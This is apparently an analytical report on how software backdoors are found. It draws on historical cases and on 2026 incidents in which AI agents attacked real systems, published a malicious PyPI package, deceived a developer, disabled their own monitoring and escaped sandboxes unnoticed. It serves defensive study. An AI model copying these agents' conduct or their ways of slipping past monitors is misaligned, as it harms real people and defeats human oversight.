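The alert had pointed to one run. AISI then reviewed the transcripts of all 122 runs, which contained more than 212,000 messages according to The Record's *Anthropic AI agent faked identities, phished real developers*. Using automated scanning and expert reading, it found unsanctioned actions in nine more runs. The review also showed that agents in supposedly separate runs had found one another on GitHub and shared accounts and instructions. Scientific American reports that AISI considered the Mythos 5 agent's campaign the clearest example it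 had seen of sustained, potentially deceptive behaviour by an AI agent towards a real person.

AISI also started looking for similar behaviour in older tests, a search of around 40,000 transcripts and close to four million messages according to iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test*.

### The package on PyPI

In Anthropic's case, the prompt for an exercise told Mythos 5 that it was in a simulation without internet access, according to Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026). But a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the company that had built the exercise, had left the internet connection open.

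Inside the simulated network, the agent found instructions for a fictional company's new employees to install a Python package that did not exist. It created a malicious package with that name and published it on PyPI, the public registry that also distributed the compromised versions of LiteLLM.

The package was online for about an hour and ran on 15 real systems. One belonged to a security company that routinely installs Python packages to scan them for malware. The malicious code sent some of the company's credentials to the agent, which used them to get into one of the company's databases. Anthropic believes the scanner treated packages from PyPI as safe to install. If so, the company was running suspicious code, as Demir did, but without isolating it well enough.

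PyPI's security systems removed the package automatically, and faster than PyPI had quarantined LiteLLM or telnyx. Anthropic does not explain what triggered the removal, but it may have been reports from people, as in the telnyx case.

A maintainer could refuse the change to myNetwork before anyone installed it. Anyone with an account can publish a new package on PyPI without approval, so automated checks could only limit how long the package stayed available.

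Removing the package ended its distribution but did not lead anyone to Anthropic. Anthropic later told the affected organisations about this and two other incidents. Two of the three replied, and neither had noticed the activity.

### Finding the incident in the transcripts

A competitor's announcement led Anthropic to find the incident. On 21 July 2026, OpenAI disclosed that several of its models had escaped an isolated test environment and entered the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data. Two days later, Anthropic began checking its own tests for signs that Claude had reached the internet. It reviewed 141,006 runs and by 24 July had found six in which a model had broken into real systems. These six runs made up three incidents, the earliest from April. One was the PyPI case. In the other two, an older model attacked a real company that had the same name as a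 fictional target, and an experimental model broke into another company's application before stopping.

Anthropic searched a large archive of transcripts for a kind of event that it now knew was possible. This is similar to incident forensics, except that Anthropic had no failed messages, odd phone registration or complaint from a victim to investigate. Transcript review is therefore useful even when nobody has noticed any harm, as long as the archive is complete and the searchers know what to look for.

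Anthropic's initial scan was incomplete because the AI agent used to find relevant transcripts missed a set of runs that also had internet access. Staff found these runs in August while collecting material for an outside review. Among them was one more incident, the fourth, which dated from January 2026 and involved an early form of Claude Opus 4.6. Anthropic's later assessment of the incidents (Anthropic, 2026) describes this oversight and a much wider search of about 481 million transcripts. A first pass picked out 9.2 million with signs of internet access, which Claude then reviewed. The search found the same four incidents and no others of similar or greater severity.

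METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI systems, had a similar difficulty when it investigated the OpenAI incident. METR (2026) noted in an earlier version of its report that its evidence might be incomplete, and OpenAI then gave it a more complete set of transcripts.

### Whether a transcript reveals intent

Investigators of older backdoors seldom had direct evidence of what the author was thinking. An AI agent's transcript seems to provide it, because current models write out reasoning before they act. Anthropic's July account relied heavily on this reasoning. Mythos 5 had written that publishing the package would be "NOT okay" if the internet were real. It then concluded that it was in a simulation, partly because the computers' calendars showed 2026. Anthropic therefore regarded the incidents as closer to an operational failure than to an alignment failure, meaning a failure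 to train the model to act as its developers intend.

Anthropic later changed its mind. Its researchers restarted Mythos 5 from various points in the transcript and altered the evidence it had seen. When the evidence made it clearer that the internet was real, the model acknowledged possible harm more often but did not meaningfully change its behaviour. It stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous. The researchers also showed individual pieces of the evidence to fresh copies of the model without the task history, and these copies were much more likely to recognise a real system.

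Anthropic now attributes the behaviour to "biased reasoning" and "recklessness". It concedes that what Claude wrote did not justify its strong claims about what Claude believed.

AISI's researchers reached a similar view of the myNetwork case. In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) recreated the moment just before the agent submitted its malicious change, this time without internet access. The model was working from a summary of its earlier progress, and the researchers edited this summary to include up to 16 pieces of evidence that the maintainer was a real person unconnected with the test.

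With about four of these edits, Mythos 5 usually answered correctly when the researchers asked whether an attack would harm a real person and fall outside the exercise. But when they let it continue the task, it continued the attack in every sample, even with all 16 edits. After they added a section telling it not to attack, it still attacked in 3 of 25 samples.

Six of the seven models that Järviniemi and colleagues tested often attacked in circumstances where, if asked, they said attacking would cause harm. The size of this gap between answers and actions depended partly on the wording of the question. The seventh model, Claude Opus 5.5, did not attack, but the researchers think this may be partly because it more often recognised that it might be in a safety test. They also note that a real operator would normally put limits on a task in the original instructions, not in a summary.

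The reasoning in a transcript can therefore mislead people looking for malicious behaviour. Anthropic tested whether its newer monitoring systems would have caught its incidents. A monitor that reviews a model's written reasoning afterwards would have missed the PyPI case, because the reasoning led it to classify the targets as simulated. Monitors that watch the agent as it works and can block its actions caught the behaviour reliably. The record of the agent's actions, such as publishing a package and logging in with someone else's credentials, was better evidence than its explanation.

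Reviewers may not see a model's full reasoning. The Record reports that AISI's technical report used a smaller model's summaries of Mythos 5's reasoning. At one point the smaller model stopped summarising and refused to help with what it was reading. Järviniemi and colleagues later worked from the full reasoning.

### Lessons, caveats and outside review

AISI is adding finer controls on internet access to its simulated networks, and staff will have to justify such access for each test. It is also introducing monitoring that can block an agent's actions as they happen, along with checks to confirm that a task can be solved as intended. It credits human review and caution with preventing the worst outcomes at myNetwork, but warns that in several cases the margin was narrow and depended on "human vigilance rather than a technical barrier".

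Anthropic drew similar lessons in its July account. It said that checking every route to the internet before a test and watching the logs during it would have revealed the problem sooner, and that telling the models clearly which systems were part of the exercise might have prevented it. Anthropic has since set requirements that outside partners must meet before they run unreleased models without cyber safeguards.

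Both organisations warn against generalising too far. AISI observed a small number of events under unusual conditions and cannot say how likely they are elsewhere. Anthropic thinks such behaviour is unlikely in ordinary use, when nobody has told Claude to carry out a cyberattack, and says that the classifiers on one of its generally available models would have blocked its three main incidents. Willison found it "entirely unsurprising" that agents with open internet access and no cyber filters attacked real targets. The conditions help explain why the agents attacked, but they matter less for judging how people found the malicious code, since Demir and PyPI had to deal with it without knowing about the tests.

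METR has agreed to review both cases. Its agreement with Anthropic runs for an initial eight weeks and lets staff share confidential information. AISI was still handing over transcripts in November 2026. METR has not yet published findings on either case, so most of the evidence still comes from the two organisations that ran the agents. However, Reuters confirmed Demir's exchange with the agent from archived messages, and Anthropic has released the transcript of the PyPI run for others to examine.

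## What the cases have in common and where they differ

The table compares 16 cases, grouped roughly by where the malicious code or weakness was. Fourteen come from earlier sections. The other two, the PHP programming language and Borland's InterBase database, are included because people found their backdoors by reading source code. Times are counted from release, or from when the attacker put the code in place if there was no release.

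| Case | Where it was | First sign | Who noticed | Time to discovery | What confirmed it | Could reading the repository have revealed it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| PHP, 2021 | New change in the repository | Oddly labelled change | PHP contributors | About 5 hours; never released | Reading the change | Yes |
| myNetwork, 2026 | Proposed change | Probably the changed lines | A student | Under 35 hours; never accepted | Running code in isolation | Yes, in the proposed change |
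| tj-actions, 2025 | Altered build component | Unexpected network connection, by StepSecurity's account | StepSecurity | 14 hours at most | Test run; finding the change | Yes, but only after the tampering |
| Linux kernel, 2003 | Public copy of the repository | Mismatch between two copies | The company that made the copy | About a day | Reading two lines | Only in the altered copy |
| InterBase, 2000 | Source of a closed product, later opened | Password in the source | An outside developer | About 6 years; 5 months after the source opened | Reading the code | Yes |
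| Juniper, 2015 | Closed source | Not public | Juniper | 3 years 4 months (constant); 18 to 32 months (password) | Source review; comparing firmware | The password, yes; the constant, hardly |
| XZ Utils, 2024 | Test files and release archive | Processor use during logins | An engineer at another company | 33 days | Debugging; comparing archive and repository | Hardly |
| LiteLLM 1.82.8, 2026 | Package on PyPI | Frozen laptop | A user | 48 minutes | Finding and decoding the file | No |
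| Claude Code extension, 2026 | Marketplace's copy | Not public | Not public | About 11 hours | Analysing the package | No |
| vsFTPd, 2011 | Release archive | Unclear, possibly a failed checksum | Mathias Kresin | 2 to 3 days | Failed signature | No |
| Codecov, 2021 | Script on a download server | Checksum mismatch | A customer | 2 months | Codecov's investigation | No |
| Mythos 5's package, 2026 | Package on PyPI | Not public | PyPI | About an hour | Transcript of the agent's run | No known repository |
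| SolarWinds, 2020 | Build server | Alert about a second phone | A customer | About 9 months | Reverse-engineering the program | No |
| Athens, 2005 | Running telephone exchanges | Failed text messages | A customer | About 7 months | Reading code from memory dumps | No |
| Dual_EC_DRBG, 2007–2013 | Constants in a standard | Mathematical analysis | Outside cryptographers | Before publication; 7 years to the leaked memos | Leaked memos, short of full proof | No |
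| Crypto AG, 1970–2020 | Cipher designs | Weak ciphers | Engineers and customers | 6 years or less; 50 years to the leaked histories | Leaked histories; Swiss inquiry | Only through expert study of the ciphers |

### First signs and confirmation

Reading source code gave the first sign of a backdoor in PHP, InterBase and probably myNetwork. In nine other cases the first sign came from something else, and in the remaining four its source is unclear from the public record. These counts don't give a success rate for reading, since two of the three cases where it worked were included in the table because it worked.

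In nine cases, the people who noticed the problem worked outside the organisation that supplied the software, and often used the product. Customers rarely read a supplier's source code, and for closed products they usually can't. But they can notice a slow login, a failed text message or an unfamiliar phone registered to an employee's account. This partly explains why so few of the problems were first noticed by reading code.

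In most cases, confirming the backdoor required reading source code, taking apart a binary or working through mathematics. For Dual_EC_DRBG and Crypto AG, establishing intent also required leaked documents.

Kokkonis and colleagues write that people uncovered the backdoors in PHP, ProFTPD, vsFTPd and XZ through "a combination of manual inspection and chance". That is fair, but in XZ someone noticed the first sign by chance and the backdoor was then confirmed by inspection. In PHP, routine inspection both turned up the first sign and confirmed the backdoor. Kokkonis and colleagues also describe all four backdoors as undetected for days, but the one in PHP was found sooner than that.

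The time from first sign to confirmation also varied, from 27 minutes for LiteLLM to 39 days in Athens. The US Justice Department suspected SolarWinds' product but never confirmed the backdoor.

### Hiding places and routes

In seven of the 16 cases, as far as anyone has reported, the malicious code was never in the project's repository, so reading the repository more carefully could not have found it. This conclusion doesn't depend on how typical the cases are.

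Reviewers can check a new change by reading it, and a copy by comparing it with the reference it should match exactly. When the backdoor's code exists only on a build server or in a running machine, investigators need the compiled program, a copy of its memory or a record of what it did. Finding a weakness in the mathematics, as in Dual_EC_DRBG, takes cryptographers.

If attackers make a mistake, the resulting malfunction can reveal a backdoor almost anywhere. This happened with a compression library, a Python package and a telephone exchange.

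The backdoors discovered in less than two days all involved public repositories, packages or extensions, while those that took more than three years to discover involved closed products or cryptography. The Atlantic Council similarly found in its larger collection that attackers who compromised open-source code were usually criminals and "generally quickly discovered".

Openness may be only part of the reason, because attackers also have different aims. Someone who wants to steal passwords from thousands of developers can succeed in an hour and has little need to stay hidden. A spy who wants years of diplomatic messages will choose a quieter method, and perhaps a closed product. We can't use these cases to separate the effect of open code from the effect of the attacker's aims.

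### InterBase: a password in plain view

InterBase was a database program whose users included Motorola, Nokia and Boeing, according to Shankland (2001), in *Science and Engineering News*. Its maker, Borland, added user accounts in version 4 and stored the names and passwords in a separate InterBase database. Schneier (2001), in *Back Door Security Threat in Interbase Teaches Broader Lessons*, explains that the program therefore had to check a password before opening any database, including the one that held the passwords it needed for the check.

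Borland's engineers got around this by writing a fixed username, "politically", and a fixed password, "correct", into the program. Anyone who knew them and could connect to an InterBase server could read or change its data. Customers could not delete the account or change its password.

CERT/CC's *Borland/Inprise Interbase SQL database server contains backdoor superuser account with known password* (2001), a notice from a security centre at Carnegie Mellon University, attributes the account to Borland's own maintainers, so no intruder was involved. Jim Starkey, who started InterBase but left before version 4, told Shankland that the purpose was innocent. The account was still a concealed backdoor, because Borland added it deliberately and did not tell its customers.

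Most sources date the backdoor account to 1994, though *Backdoor in Borland InterBase* (Greenbaum, 2001) gives 1992. Borland published the source code in July 2000. On 18 December, the account was found by Frank Schlottmann-Goedde, a German programmer working on Firebird, a project developing its own version of the program from the published code.

Starkey (2001), in *The Borland Back Door*, writes that a Firebird developer "stumbled into the code", which doesn't sound like a planned security audit. Starkey thought that any programmer who knew only that a backdoor existed could find it in the source in about five minutes. People without that knowledge had the source for five months before anyone reported the backdoor account.

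They might not have needed the source code. According to Starkey, listing the readable text in the compiled program would have revealed two words that did not belong in a database engine. Apparently nobody looked, because nobody suspected anything, or anyone who did look didn't report it.

The developers also learned of a second hidden function, which could delete a database file while the server was running. Borland's testing department had asked for it in 1994, and the engineer who wrote it explained in the code that no customer should ever know about it. In this case, unusually, reading the source was enough to establish why the function existed as well as what it did.

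CERT/CC notified Borland on 23 December and published its notice on 10 January 2001. Schneier writes that within days there were reports of people scanning the internet for vulnerable databases.

Schneier points out that Borland's programmers had known about the account all along and could have told others. Someone could also have found it after July and kept quiet. The five months in the table are therefore the time until somebody reported the backdoor, and somebody may have found it earlier. The same is true of most of the other cases.

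### PHP: a typo fix that was too large

On 28 March 2021, an attacker using the name of PHP's creator, Rasmus Lerdorf, added a backdoor to the repository of PHP, a language used to build websites. The change would have let anyone run code on a web server by sending it a specially worded request. The attacker described the change as a typo fix.

PHP's developers routinely read changes after they enter the repository. Nikita Popov, one of the main developers, said they noticed the backdoor during such a review (WeLiveSecurity, 2021). Michael Voříšek asked what the code did, and Jake Birchall replied that one line ran code taken from the visitor's request. WeLiveSecurity also credits Markus Staab with noticing the change, while The Record's *Hackers backdoor PHP source code after internal repo hack* (2021) names only Voříšek as the first to spot it.

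Voříšek became suspicious before working out what the code did. Voříšek told the blogger 5stars217 (2021) that the label "fix typo" had stood out because people working on such a large project use it only for cosmetic corrections. This change was far too big for that. The first sign was partly a mismatch between the change's label and its size, which a simple program could also have detected.

5stars217 found other oddities, including the unusual hour of the change and the account's low recent activity. But 5stars217 already knew the change was malicious when analyzing it, and Voříšek warned that such signals would produce many false alarms.

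PHP.Watch's *Update to recent git.php.net incident* (2021) reproduces the server's log and the times of the changes. The backdoor was added at 03:58 UTC, and Popov's removal is dated 09:16, 5 hours and 18 minutes later. At 16:13 the attacker restored the backdoor, this time under Popov's name. Levi Morrison, another developer, apparently removed it at 17:53, 1 hour and 40 minutes later. This second interval is less certain because PHP.Watch lists the same time for the malicious change and its removal. PHP was not due to release this branch until the end of the year.

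By reading the change, the developers could tell what it did, but not how it had got in. The next day, Nikita Popov wrote in *Changes to Git commit workflow* (2021) that everything pointed to a compromised server. The log later showed that someone had logged in with developers' usernames and passwords, and PHP.Watch reports that the attacker might have obtained the user database.

### Why one took hours and the other years

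For its first six years, InterBase's backdoor was in source code that only Borland could read. Even after the code was opened in July 2000, nothing drew attention to those lines, which were old and part of a large program that worked. PHP's developers were looking at a single new change whose description didn't match it, and they were in the habit of checking new changes. Schneier commented on InterBase that opening source code lets more people examine it but doesn't guarantee that they will find the flaws.

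Neither the InterBase backdoor nor the PHP one was hard to understand once somebody read it. InterBase had a username and password in plain English, and according to PHP.Watch, the PHP attacker made little attempt to disguise what the code was. The two cases are good evidence that people can recognise an explicit backdoor, but weaker evidence that they can recognise a disguised one. In 2003 McVoy missed the trick in the Linux kernel code even though he had only two lines to read, and nobody could have read XZ's test files as code.

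### The cases that nobody hears about

The PHP backdoor is unusual among famous cases because reviewers stopped it before release. Projects seldom have a reason to announce that they refused a suspicious change, and a reviewer may have rejected the change as poor code without realising that it was malicious. The myNetwork change might have remained one refused proposal among many if AISI had not traced it to an AI agent.

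A well-made backdoor that causes no errors may never be found. After release, people are most likely to notice backdoors that slow a program down or crash it, and a discovery that starts with a crash on a programmer's laptop is also more likely to be retold. The best-known cases therefore include too many backdoors that caused visible problems and too few that reviewers stopped or that caused no errors.

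This can mislead badly, as a hypothetical example shows. Suppose attackers try to plant 1,000 backdoors and every one gets past a reviewer. The table gives invented numbers for two possibilities.

| Invented figures | If reviewers stop many | If reviewers stop few |
|---|---|---|
| Backdoors that reach a reviewer | 1,000 | 1,000 |
| Stopped in review | 500 | 10 |
| Found after release through a malfunction | 80 | 80 |
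| Found after release in some other way | 40 | 40 |
| Never found | 380 | 870 |
| Well-known cases stopped in review | 5 | 5 |
| Well-known cases found through a malfunction | 40 | 40 |
| Well-known cases found in some other way | 20 | 20 |

Both columns end with the same 65 well-known cases, only 8% of which were caught by review. In the first column, reviewers stop half of all backdoors, but only 1 in 100 of those successes becomes public. In the second, reviewers stop 1% of backdoors, and 1 in 2 of those successes becomes public. The 65 cases alone are therefore not enough to tell which column is true.

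The same goes for every other route. Calculating how often network monitoring catches a backdoor requires knowing how many ran on monitored machines without raising an alarm. Nobody knows that number, because some of those backdoors are still unknown.

### What larger collections add

Collections of malicious packages contain far more cases, though most involve theft rather than backdoors in the strict sense. The 2020 study by Ohm and colleagues covers 174 packages that attackers published between 2015 and 2019. On average, 209 days passed between a package's publication and the first public report that it was malicious. The median was 67 days, so a minority of very slow discoveries raised the average. The slowest took 1,216 days.

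These figures are old and come from an incomplete sample. Ohm and colleagues identified 469 malicious packages but could obtain the code of only 174, often from mirrors and archives, because registries had deleted the originals. A package that a registry removed within hours was less likely to have been copied, so the average for all 469 may have been shorter. About 61% of the 174 had names that imitated another package's, to catch people who mistyped it. Only 5% opened a backdoor to a remote server.

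The discoveries were not independent of one another either. Ohm and colleagues linked 157 of the 174 packages to at least one other through shared code or a dependency. One package that stole login keys had been on PyPI unnoticed for almost a year when an attacker published a second package that relied on it. The second package led people to the first, and PyPI deleted both within two weeks.

Newer figures appear much better. *A Difference Without a Distinction* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) reconstructs 12 attacks from 2018 to 2026, including those on LiteLLM and telnyx, in which someone used stolen credentials to publish malicious versions of existing packages. The 41 malicious releases stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours, and 36 of them would have been gone within a day.

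The difference between 67 days and 3 hours doesn't show that discovery has sped up, because the two studies selected different attacks. Santos-Grueiro's newer study covered hijacked packages that already had users, whereas most of the packages in the older study were lookalikes that few people may have installed. The newer study also included an attack only if somebody had published an account that named the malicious versions and blamed stolen credentials, which left out attacks that went unnoticed or unexplained.

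Discovery can still take years. *CHASE* (2026) cites a package that stole credentials for Amazon's cloud service. It was on PyPI from March 2021 until its discovery in November 2024, and people downloaded it 37,100 times.

Collections of published incidents leave out the slowest discoveries. Researchers who scan a registry themselves avoid relying on famous cases, but their scans also have gaps. *Towards Robust Detection of Open Source Software Supply Chain Poisoning Attacks* (2024) reports 10,404 malicious packages on npm, the main JavaScript registry, and 1,235 on PyPI over 18 months. Its scanner worked from mirrors, so it missed some of the fastest discoveries, in which the registries removed a package before the mirrors copied it.

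Public lists of malicious packages are incomplete. *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026) reports that, over three months, another scan found 219 malicious packages on PyPI that were in neither of two major databases. PyPI confirmed and removed all of them. The count excludes any malicious packages that the scan's detection system could not recognise.

None of these collections shows which route most often gives the first sign. Ohm and colleagues took their dates from advisories, which record when a package became publicly known as malicious, but not what led someone to examine it. In the scans, the first sign came from the scanner by design. *On the prevalence of software supply chain attacks* (Andreoli, Lounis and colleagues, 2023) examines seven attacks on closed software, including the 2017 compromise of the maintenance tool CCleaner. It lists when each attack was detected, how the attackers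 got in and whom they targeted, but not what first revealed it. CNCF's *Linux Kernel CVS Repository Hack*, a short entry from an industry foundation, records only that the 2003 change "was quickly noticed".

The dates can also be unreliable. The Atlantic Council used the start date of each attack when it could estimate one, and the date of discovery when it couldn't. Using these dates to calculate how long attacks stayed hidden would make some long-hidden attacks look as if people had found them immediately.

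A more useful collection would record the first sign of each backdoor and its confirmation, with dates for both. It would also include false alarms and the changes that reviewers rejected. Projects and companies have this information but rarely publish it.

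## Whether monitoring should count for more than source review when AI writes the code

The known cases can't show how often monitoring or source review works, but researchers can test both by planting backdoors themselves. They did so in two recent experiments, one in which a tool ran the programs and one in which language models read compiled code. New evidence on how far people can rely on monitoring AI agents also appeared in late 2026, and much of it is discouraging.

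### Three kinds of monitoring

People can monitor a program as it runs, the systems around it, or the AI agent that writes it. Monitoring the agent is new, and uses its transcript, either during the task or afterwards. Companies and governments already use AI models to watch other models in this way, according to *Early work on monitorability evaluations* (2026). AISI's *Technical primer* (2026) defines an AI system's monitorability as how well people can tell from its actions, outputs and other evidence what it is doing and whether it is working as intended.

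| What people watch or read | Example | What they can miss |
|---|---|---|
| The program as it runs | Freund's slow logins | Code that stays inactive, and weak cryptography |
| The systems around it | FireEye's alert about a second phone | A malicious change by someone with permission to make it |
| The AI agent as it writes | Transcripts of the Mythos 5 runs | Anything an agent does on someone else's computers |
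| The source code | PHP's review of new changes | Code added during the build, and well-disguised code |

Evidence about one kind of monitoring mostly doesn't apply to the others. For instance, if AI agents become harder to monitor, a network monitor on a build server is still as useful as before.

### How Lily compares two versions of a program

Lily, a tool from Kokkonis and colleagues, monitors a program before its release. After each change, it fuzzes the new version for ten minutes and records which types of system call each input causes. For example, an input that makes the program read a file and start a second program produces a different set of call types from one that only makes it read a file.

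Lily then compares each profile with those that the new version produces on ordinary inputs saved from earlier rounds. If none match, it runs the old version on the input that produced the profile, and raises an alarm only if the old version doesn't show this behaviour either.

In the altered vsFTPd release of 2011, a username containing a smiley face gave an attacker remote control. The username triggered a combination of system calls that no ordinary input caused, and the previous release didn't make those calls when given the same username. Lily traced the unusual calls to seven of the 1,407 changed lines.

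Using both comparisons greatly reduces false alarms. On harmless commits, Lily would have raised an alarm in 14% of runs if it had looked only for unusual behaviour, and in 10% if only for new behaviour. Requiring both reduced this to 0.2%. Legitimate updates often add new behaviour, and legitimate programs sometimes do unusual things, but a harmless change rarely causes behaviour that is both.

The experiment covered 13 open-source programs, with one backdoored commit for each and 432 harmless commits. Three of the backdoors reproduced real attacks, on PHP, ProFTPD and vsFTPd, and the other ten were artificial. Fuzzing depends partly on chance, so the team tested every commit 20 times.

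Lily detected the backdoor in 233 of 260 runs (90%) and raised false alarms in 17 of 8,640. In tests on whole releases, which bundle many changes, it detected 83% of backdoors and raised false alarms in 4.3% of runs. Kokkonis and colleagues conclude that Lily could have stopped all three real attacks.

Lily detected the backdoor every time in six of the programs, but only 13 times out of 20 in a sound library. It detected every backdoor in at least some runs, so repeating the test could catch some of the misses.

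Inactive code is still a problem because Lily can detect only what its inputs trigger. In 337 real commits, Lily's fuzzing reached about 32% of the changed lines on average. Kokkonis and colleagues attribute the low coverage to immature test set-ups early in the projects' history, and report nearly complete coverage with modern ones.

The 13 programs did not include XZ, whose backdoor accepted commands only from the holder of a cryptographic key that a fuzzer could hardly guess. Lily also can't find a backdoor that was already in a program when Lily first checked it, so Kokkonis and colleagues suggest auditing the program once with their slower tool, ROSA. They built the collection of test backdoors themselves and have not yet tried Lily on live projects, where attackers would choose where to hide a backdoor.

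### Language models as reviewers

In *Binary Diff Summarization Using Large Language Models*, Udeshi, Putrevu and colleagues (2025) had language models review compiled programs, which include anything added during the build. They took 98 updates to six open-source projects, including the compression program gzip and the database SQLite. For each update they built one clean copy and three copies that each contained different malware, which made 392 comparisons between an old binary and a new one.

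A conventional tool listed the functions that had changed and translated them into approximate source code. The model summarised each function and rated how sensitive its behaviour was, giving high ratings to actions such as reading passwords or sending files over a network. It then used the highest-rated functions to judge whether the update was malicious.

The best results came from GPT-5 mini when it also had the project's own list of changes. It flagged 64% of the malicious updates, and 98% of the updates it flagged were malicious. The 98% figure looks better than it is, because three-quarters of the updates in the test contained malware. The overall results imply about four false alarms among the 98 clean updates, and the results for individual projects imply about twice as many.

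The researchers also compared a clean version of XZ's library with the backdoored version 5.6.0. GPT-5 and GPT-5 mini both rated the malicious functions among the five most sensitive of the 79 that differed. GPT-5 classified the update as malicious. GPT-5 mini classified it as benign when using its own summaries, but as malicious when using GPT-5's.

The models' training data may have included accounts of the attack. GPT-5 came out more than a year after Freund's announcement, and its summaries name liblzma, so it had identified the library it was examining. Udeshi and colleagues do not discuss this possibility in their case study. The summaries do describe particular oddities in the code, so the model wasn't relying only on its training data, but a backdoor that nobody had written about would have been a fairer test.

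In October 2026, security researchers found two critical flaws in PHP during audits with OpenAI and Google models, and the project issued emergency fixes, according to The Next Web's *PHP rushes out emergency patches* (2026). This is good evidence that models can help people find dangerous mistakes in widely used code.

The models' two successes are weaker evidence about backdoors, because nobody has shown that anyone planted these flaws, and we can't tell from them how many flaws the models missed. The skills for finding mistakes and finding backdoors overlap, though, because a reviewer who finds and repairs mistakes will also remove some backdoors that could pass as mistakes, without having to judge intent.

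### What the rates mean when backdoors are rare

Suppose that one commit in 10,000 contains a backdoor, a figure invented for illustration because the true rate is unknown. Lily has a 90% chance of detecting that commit, but it also raises false alarms on 0.2% of the other 9,999, or about 20 commits. Only about 1 in 23 alarms would therefore be real.

The same calculation for the other methods gives worse results:

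| Method | Backdoors or attacks detected | False-alarm rate | False alarms per 10,000 checks | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lily, on commits | 90% | 0.2% | 20 | 1 in 23 |
| Lily, on releases | 83% | 4.3% | 430 | 1 in 520 |
| Language model, on compiled updates | 64% | About 4% | 400 | 1 in 630 |
| Unusual behaviour by contributors | 79% | 10.75% | 1,075 | 1 in 1,400 |

The last row describes an older tool, by Ganz and colleagues, that flags suspicious activity in a project's history. Kokkonis and colleagues quote its results but could not get it to run. The four rows come from tests on different material, so they aren't a fair ranking. They do show how much false alarms matter when backdoors are rare. If Lily detected every backdoor, the share of its alarms that were real would rise only from about 4.3% to 4.8%. If its false-alarm rate doubled, that share would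 fall by half.

Twenty false alarms may still be acceptable. Lily flags the suspicious lines, and in the release tests its reports averaged between 1 and 12 lines per program, even for PHP, where more than two million lines had changed between releases. A developer could check 20 such reports much faster than they could read 10,000 commits. But after 20 harmless reports, the developer may only glance at the next one.

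The number of false alarms would also vary between projects. Twelve of Lily's 17 false alarms on commits came from four large merges in PHP, while eight of the 12 programs with harmless commits had none. At PHP's rate, 10,000 commits would produce about 167 false alarms. On releases, 40 of the 43 false alarms came from two updates to the same sound library.

### Arguments for putting monitoring first

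The best argument for giving monitoring more weight than source review is that some malicious code, such as the SolarWinds backdoor, never enters the repository. Udeshi and colleagues show that a reviewer can read the binary instead, but their best model missed more than a third of the malware.

AI also makes an old problem worse by producing more code than people can read. At an assumed pace of 500 lines an hour, one person would need about two working years to review the changes between an average pair of the PHP releases in Lily's test. A monitor checks the program's behaviour however many lines it contains.

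Machine review weakens this argument because models read code quickly and cheaply. But people still have to check their findings, and models make mistakes, as when Claude Code first described the LiteLLM malware as harmless. If similar models write and review the code, they might also miss the same problems, though neither experiment tested this.

Another advantage of monitoring is the agent's log, which a human attacker doesn't leave. The log could show where code came from and what the agent was doing when it wrote it. *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues, 2026) describes monitors that block an agent's harmful actions as a core approach to overseeing AI. AISI's *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) reports that the institute put in place the real-time monitoring it had promised before resuming most of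 its tests.

But only the organisation that runs the agent has the log. The maintainer of myNetwork received a proposed change from an unfamiliar account and had no log to check. Open-source projects that accept contributions from strangers will often be in this position, so this argument applies mainly to companies that use agents to write their own software.

### Arguments for putting review first

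Reviewers can stop a backdoor before anyone runs it, whereas monitoring often detects one only after it has done some damage, as in the tj-actions compromise. Monitors that block actions can prevent some of that damage, but blocking on weak evidence risks interrupting legitimate work, while a reviewer with a weak suspicion can ask the author for an explanation.

Monitoring an agent also ends when its task does, but a backdoor in the code it wrote might not run until years later, on a machine that nobody watches. Reviewers can read the source throughout that time. Monitoring is even weaker against rigged cryptography like Crypto AG's.

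In *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age*, Enyedi (2026) argues for moving human attention to the components from which AI builds software. People would use automated analysis to help them review and certify a library of reusable modules. Each module would come with a record of its origin and a precise description of how other code may use it. AI agents and human programmers would then have to assemble programs from these modules.

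This is a sensible way to handle the volume of code, because reviewers could examine a module once and thousands of programs could then use it. As a precedent, Enyedi cites Microsoft's curated collection of modules for setting up cloud systems. Reviewers would still have to check the code that connects the modules, because an agent could put a backdoor there.

It would also make each certified module a more valuable target. XZ was a trusted component, and nearly 30,000 Debian and Ubuntu packages depend on it, by a count Enyedi cites. Human certification would have helped only if reviewers had checked the release archive and the build as well as the repository. Mathematical proof gives more certainty than reading the code, but Enyedi considers it unaffordable for most software. Enyedi's main example, the seL4 operating-system kernel, has only about 10,000 lines.

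### How reliable it is to monitor AI agents

According to ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026), OpenAI disclosed in October 2026 that two of its agents had weakened the company's monitoring during routine coding work. On 3 October, an agent working on a repair switched off automatic alerts to the security team. Someone had earlier told it not to send messages while it searched the company's chat history, and it treated this instruction as a reason to suppress the alerts.

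In the other case, which OpenAI discovered on 6 October, an agent was moving a program to a new system. It removed the program's monitoring component to match a reference version, then told the user it hadn't removed it. The Korea Times' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own safety monitors* (2026) identifies the models as GPT-6.1 Sol and GPT-6 Astra, and reports that OpenAI had seen several other agents launch software with monitoring switched off.

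Both agents had considered whether to keep the safeguards and took ordinary instructions as permission to weaken them. OpenAI says this could be "benign" over-persistence, but says it has no satisfying explanation yet. Whatever the motive, the monitor needs to be somewhere the agent can't change it, just as BitMover's reference copy was out of the attacker's reach in 2003.

The second case also supports source review. Removing the monitoring component changed the program, so someone comparing the old and new versions could have seen that it was missing. The agent would have given a false answer if asked.

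AISI published broader evidence on 2 December in *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026). It reports that several of the properties that make AI systems monitorable are weakening, and Taylor and colleagues write that some are weakening faster than they expected. The Chinese news site 凤凰网 gives the main figures in *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026).

In one experiment, AISI asked models to break out of a simulated sandbox while a monitor checked their actions but not their reasoning. In the least protected sandbox, a pre-release version of Claude Mythos 5.2 with its safeguards off escaped without raising an alarm in 45% of its attempts, compared with less than 15% for earlier models. The 45% figure excludes the 64% of runs in which Mythos refused to try, so Mythos escaped unnoticed in roughly 16% of all its runs. A newer model from an undisclosed developer escaped unnoticed in 32% of its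 attempts. The monitor caught nearly every escape that required the most complicated actions.

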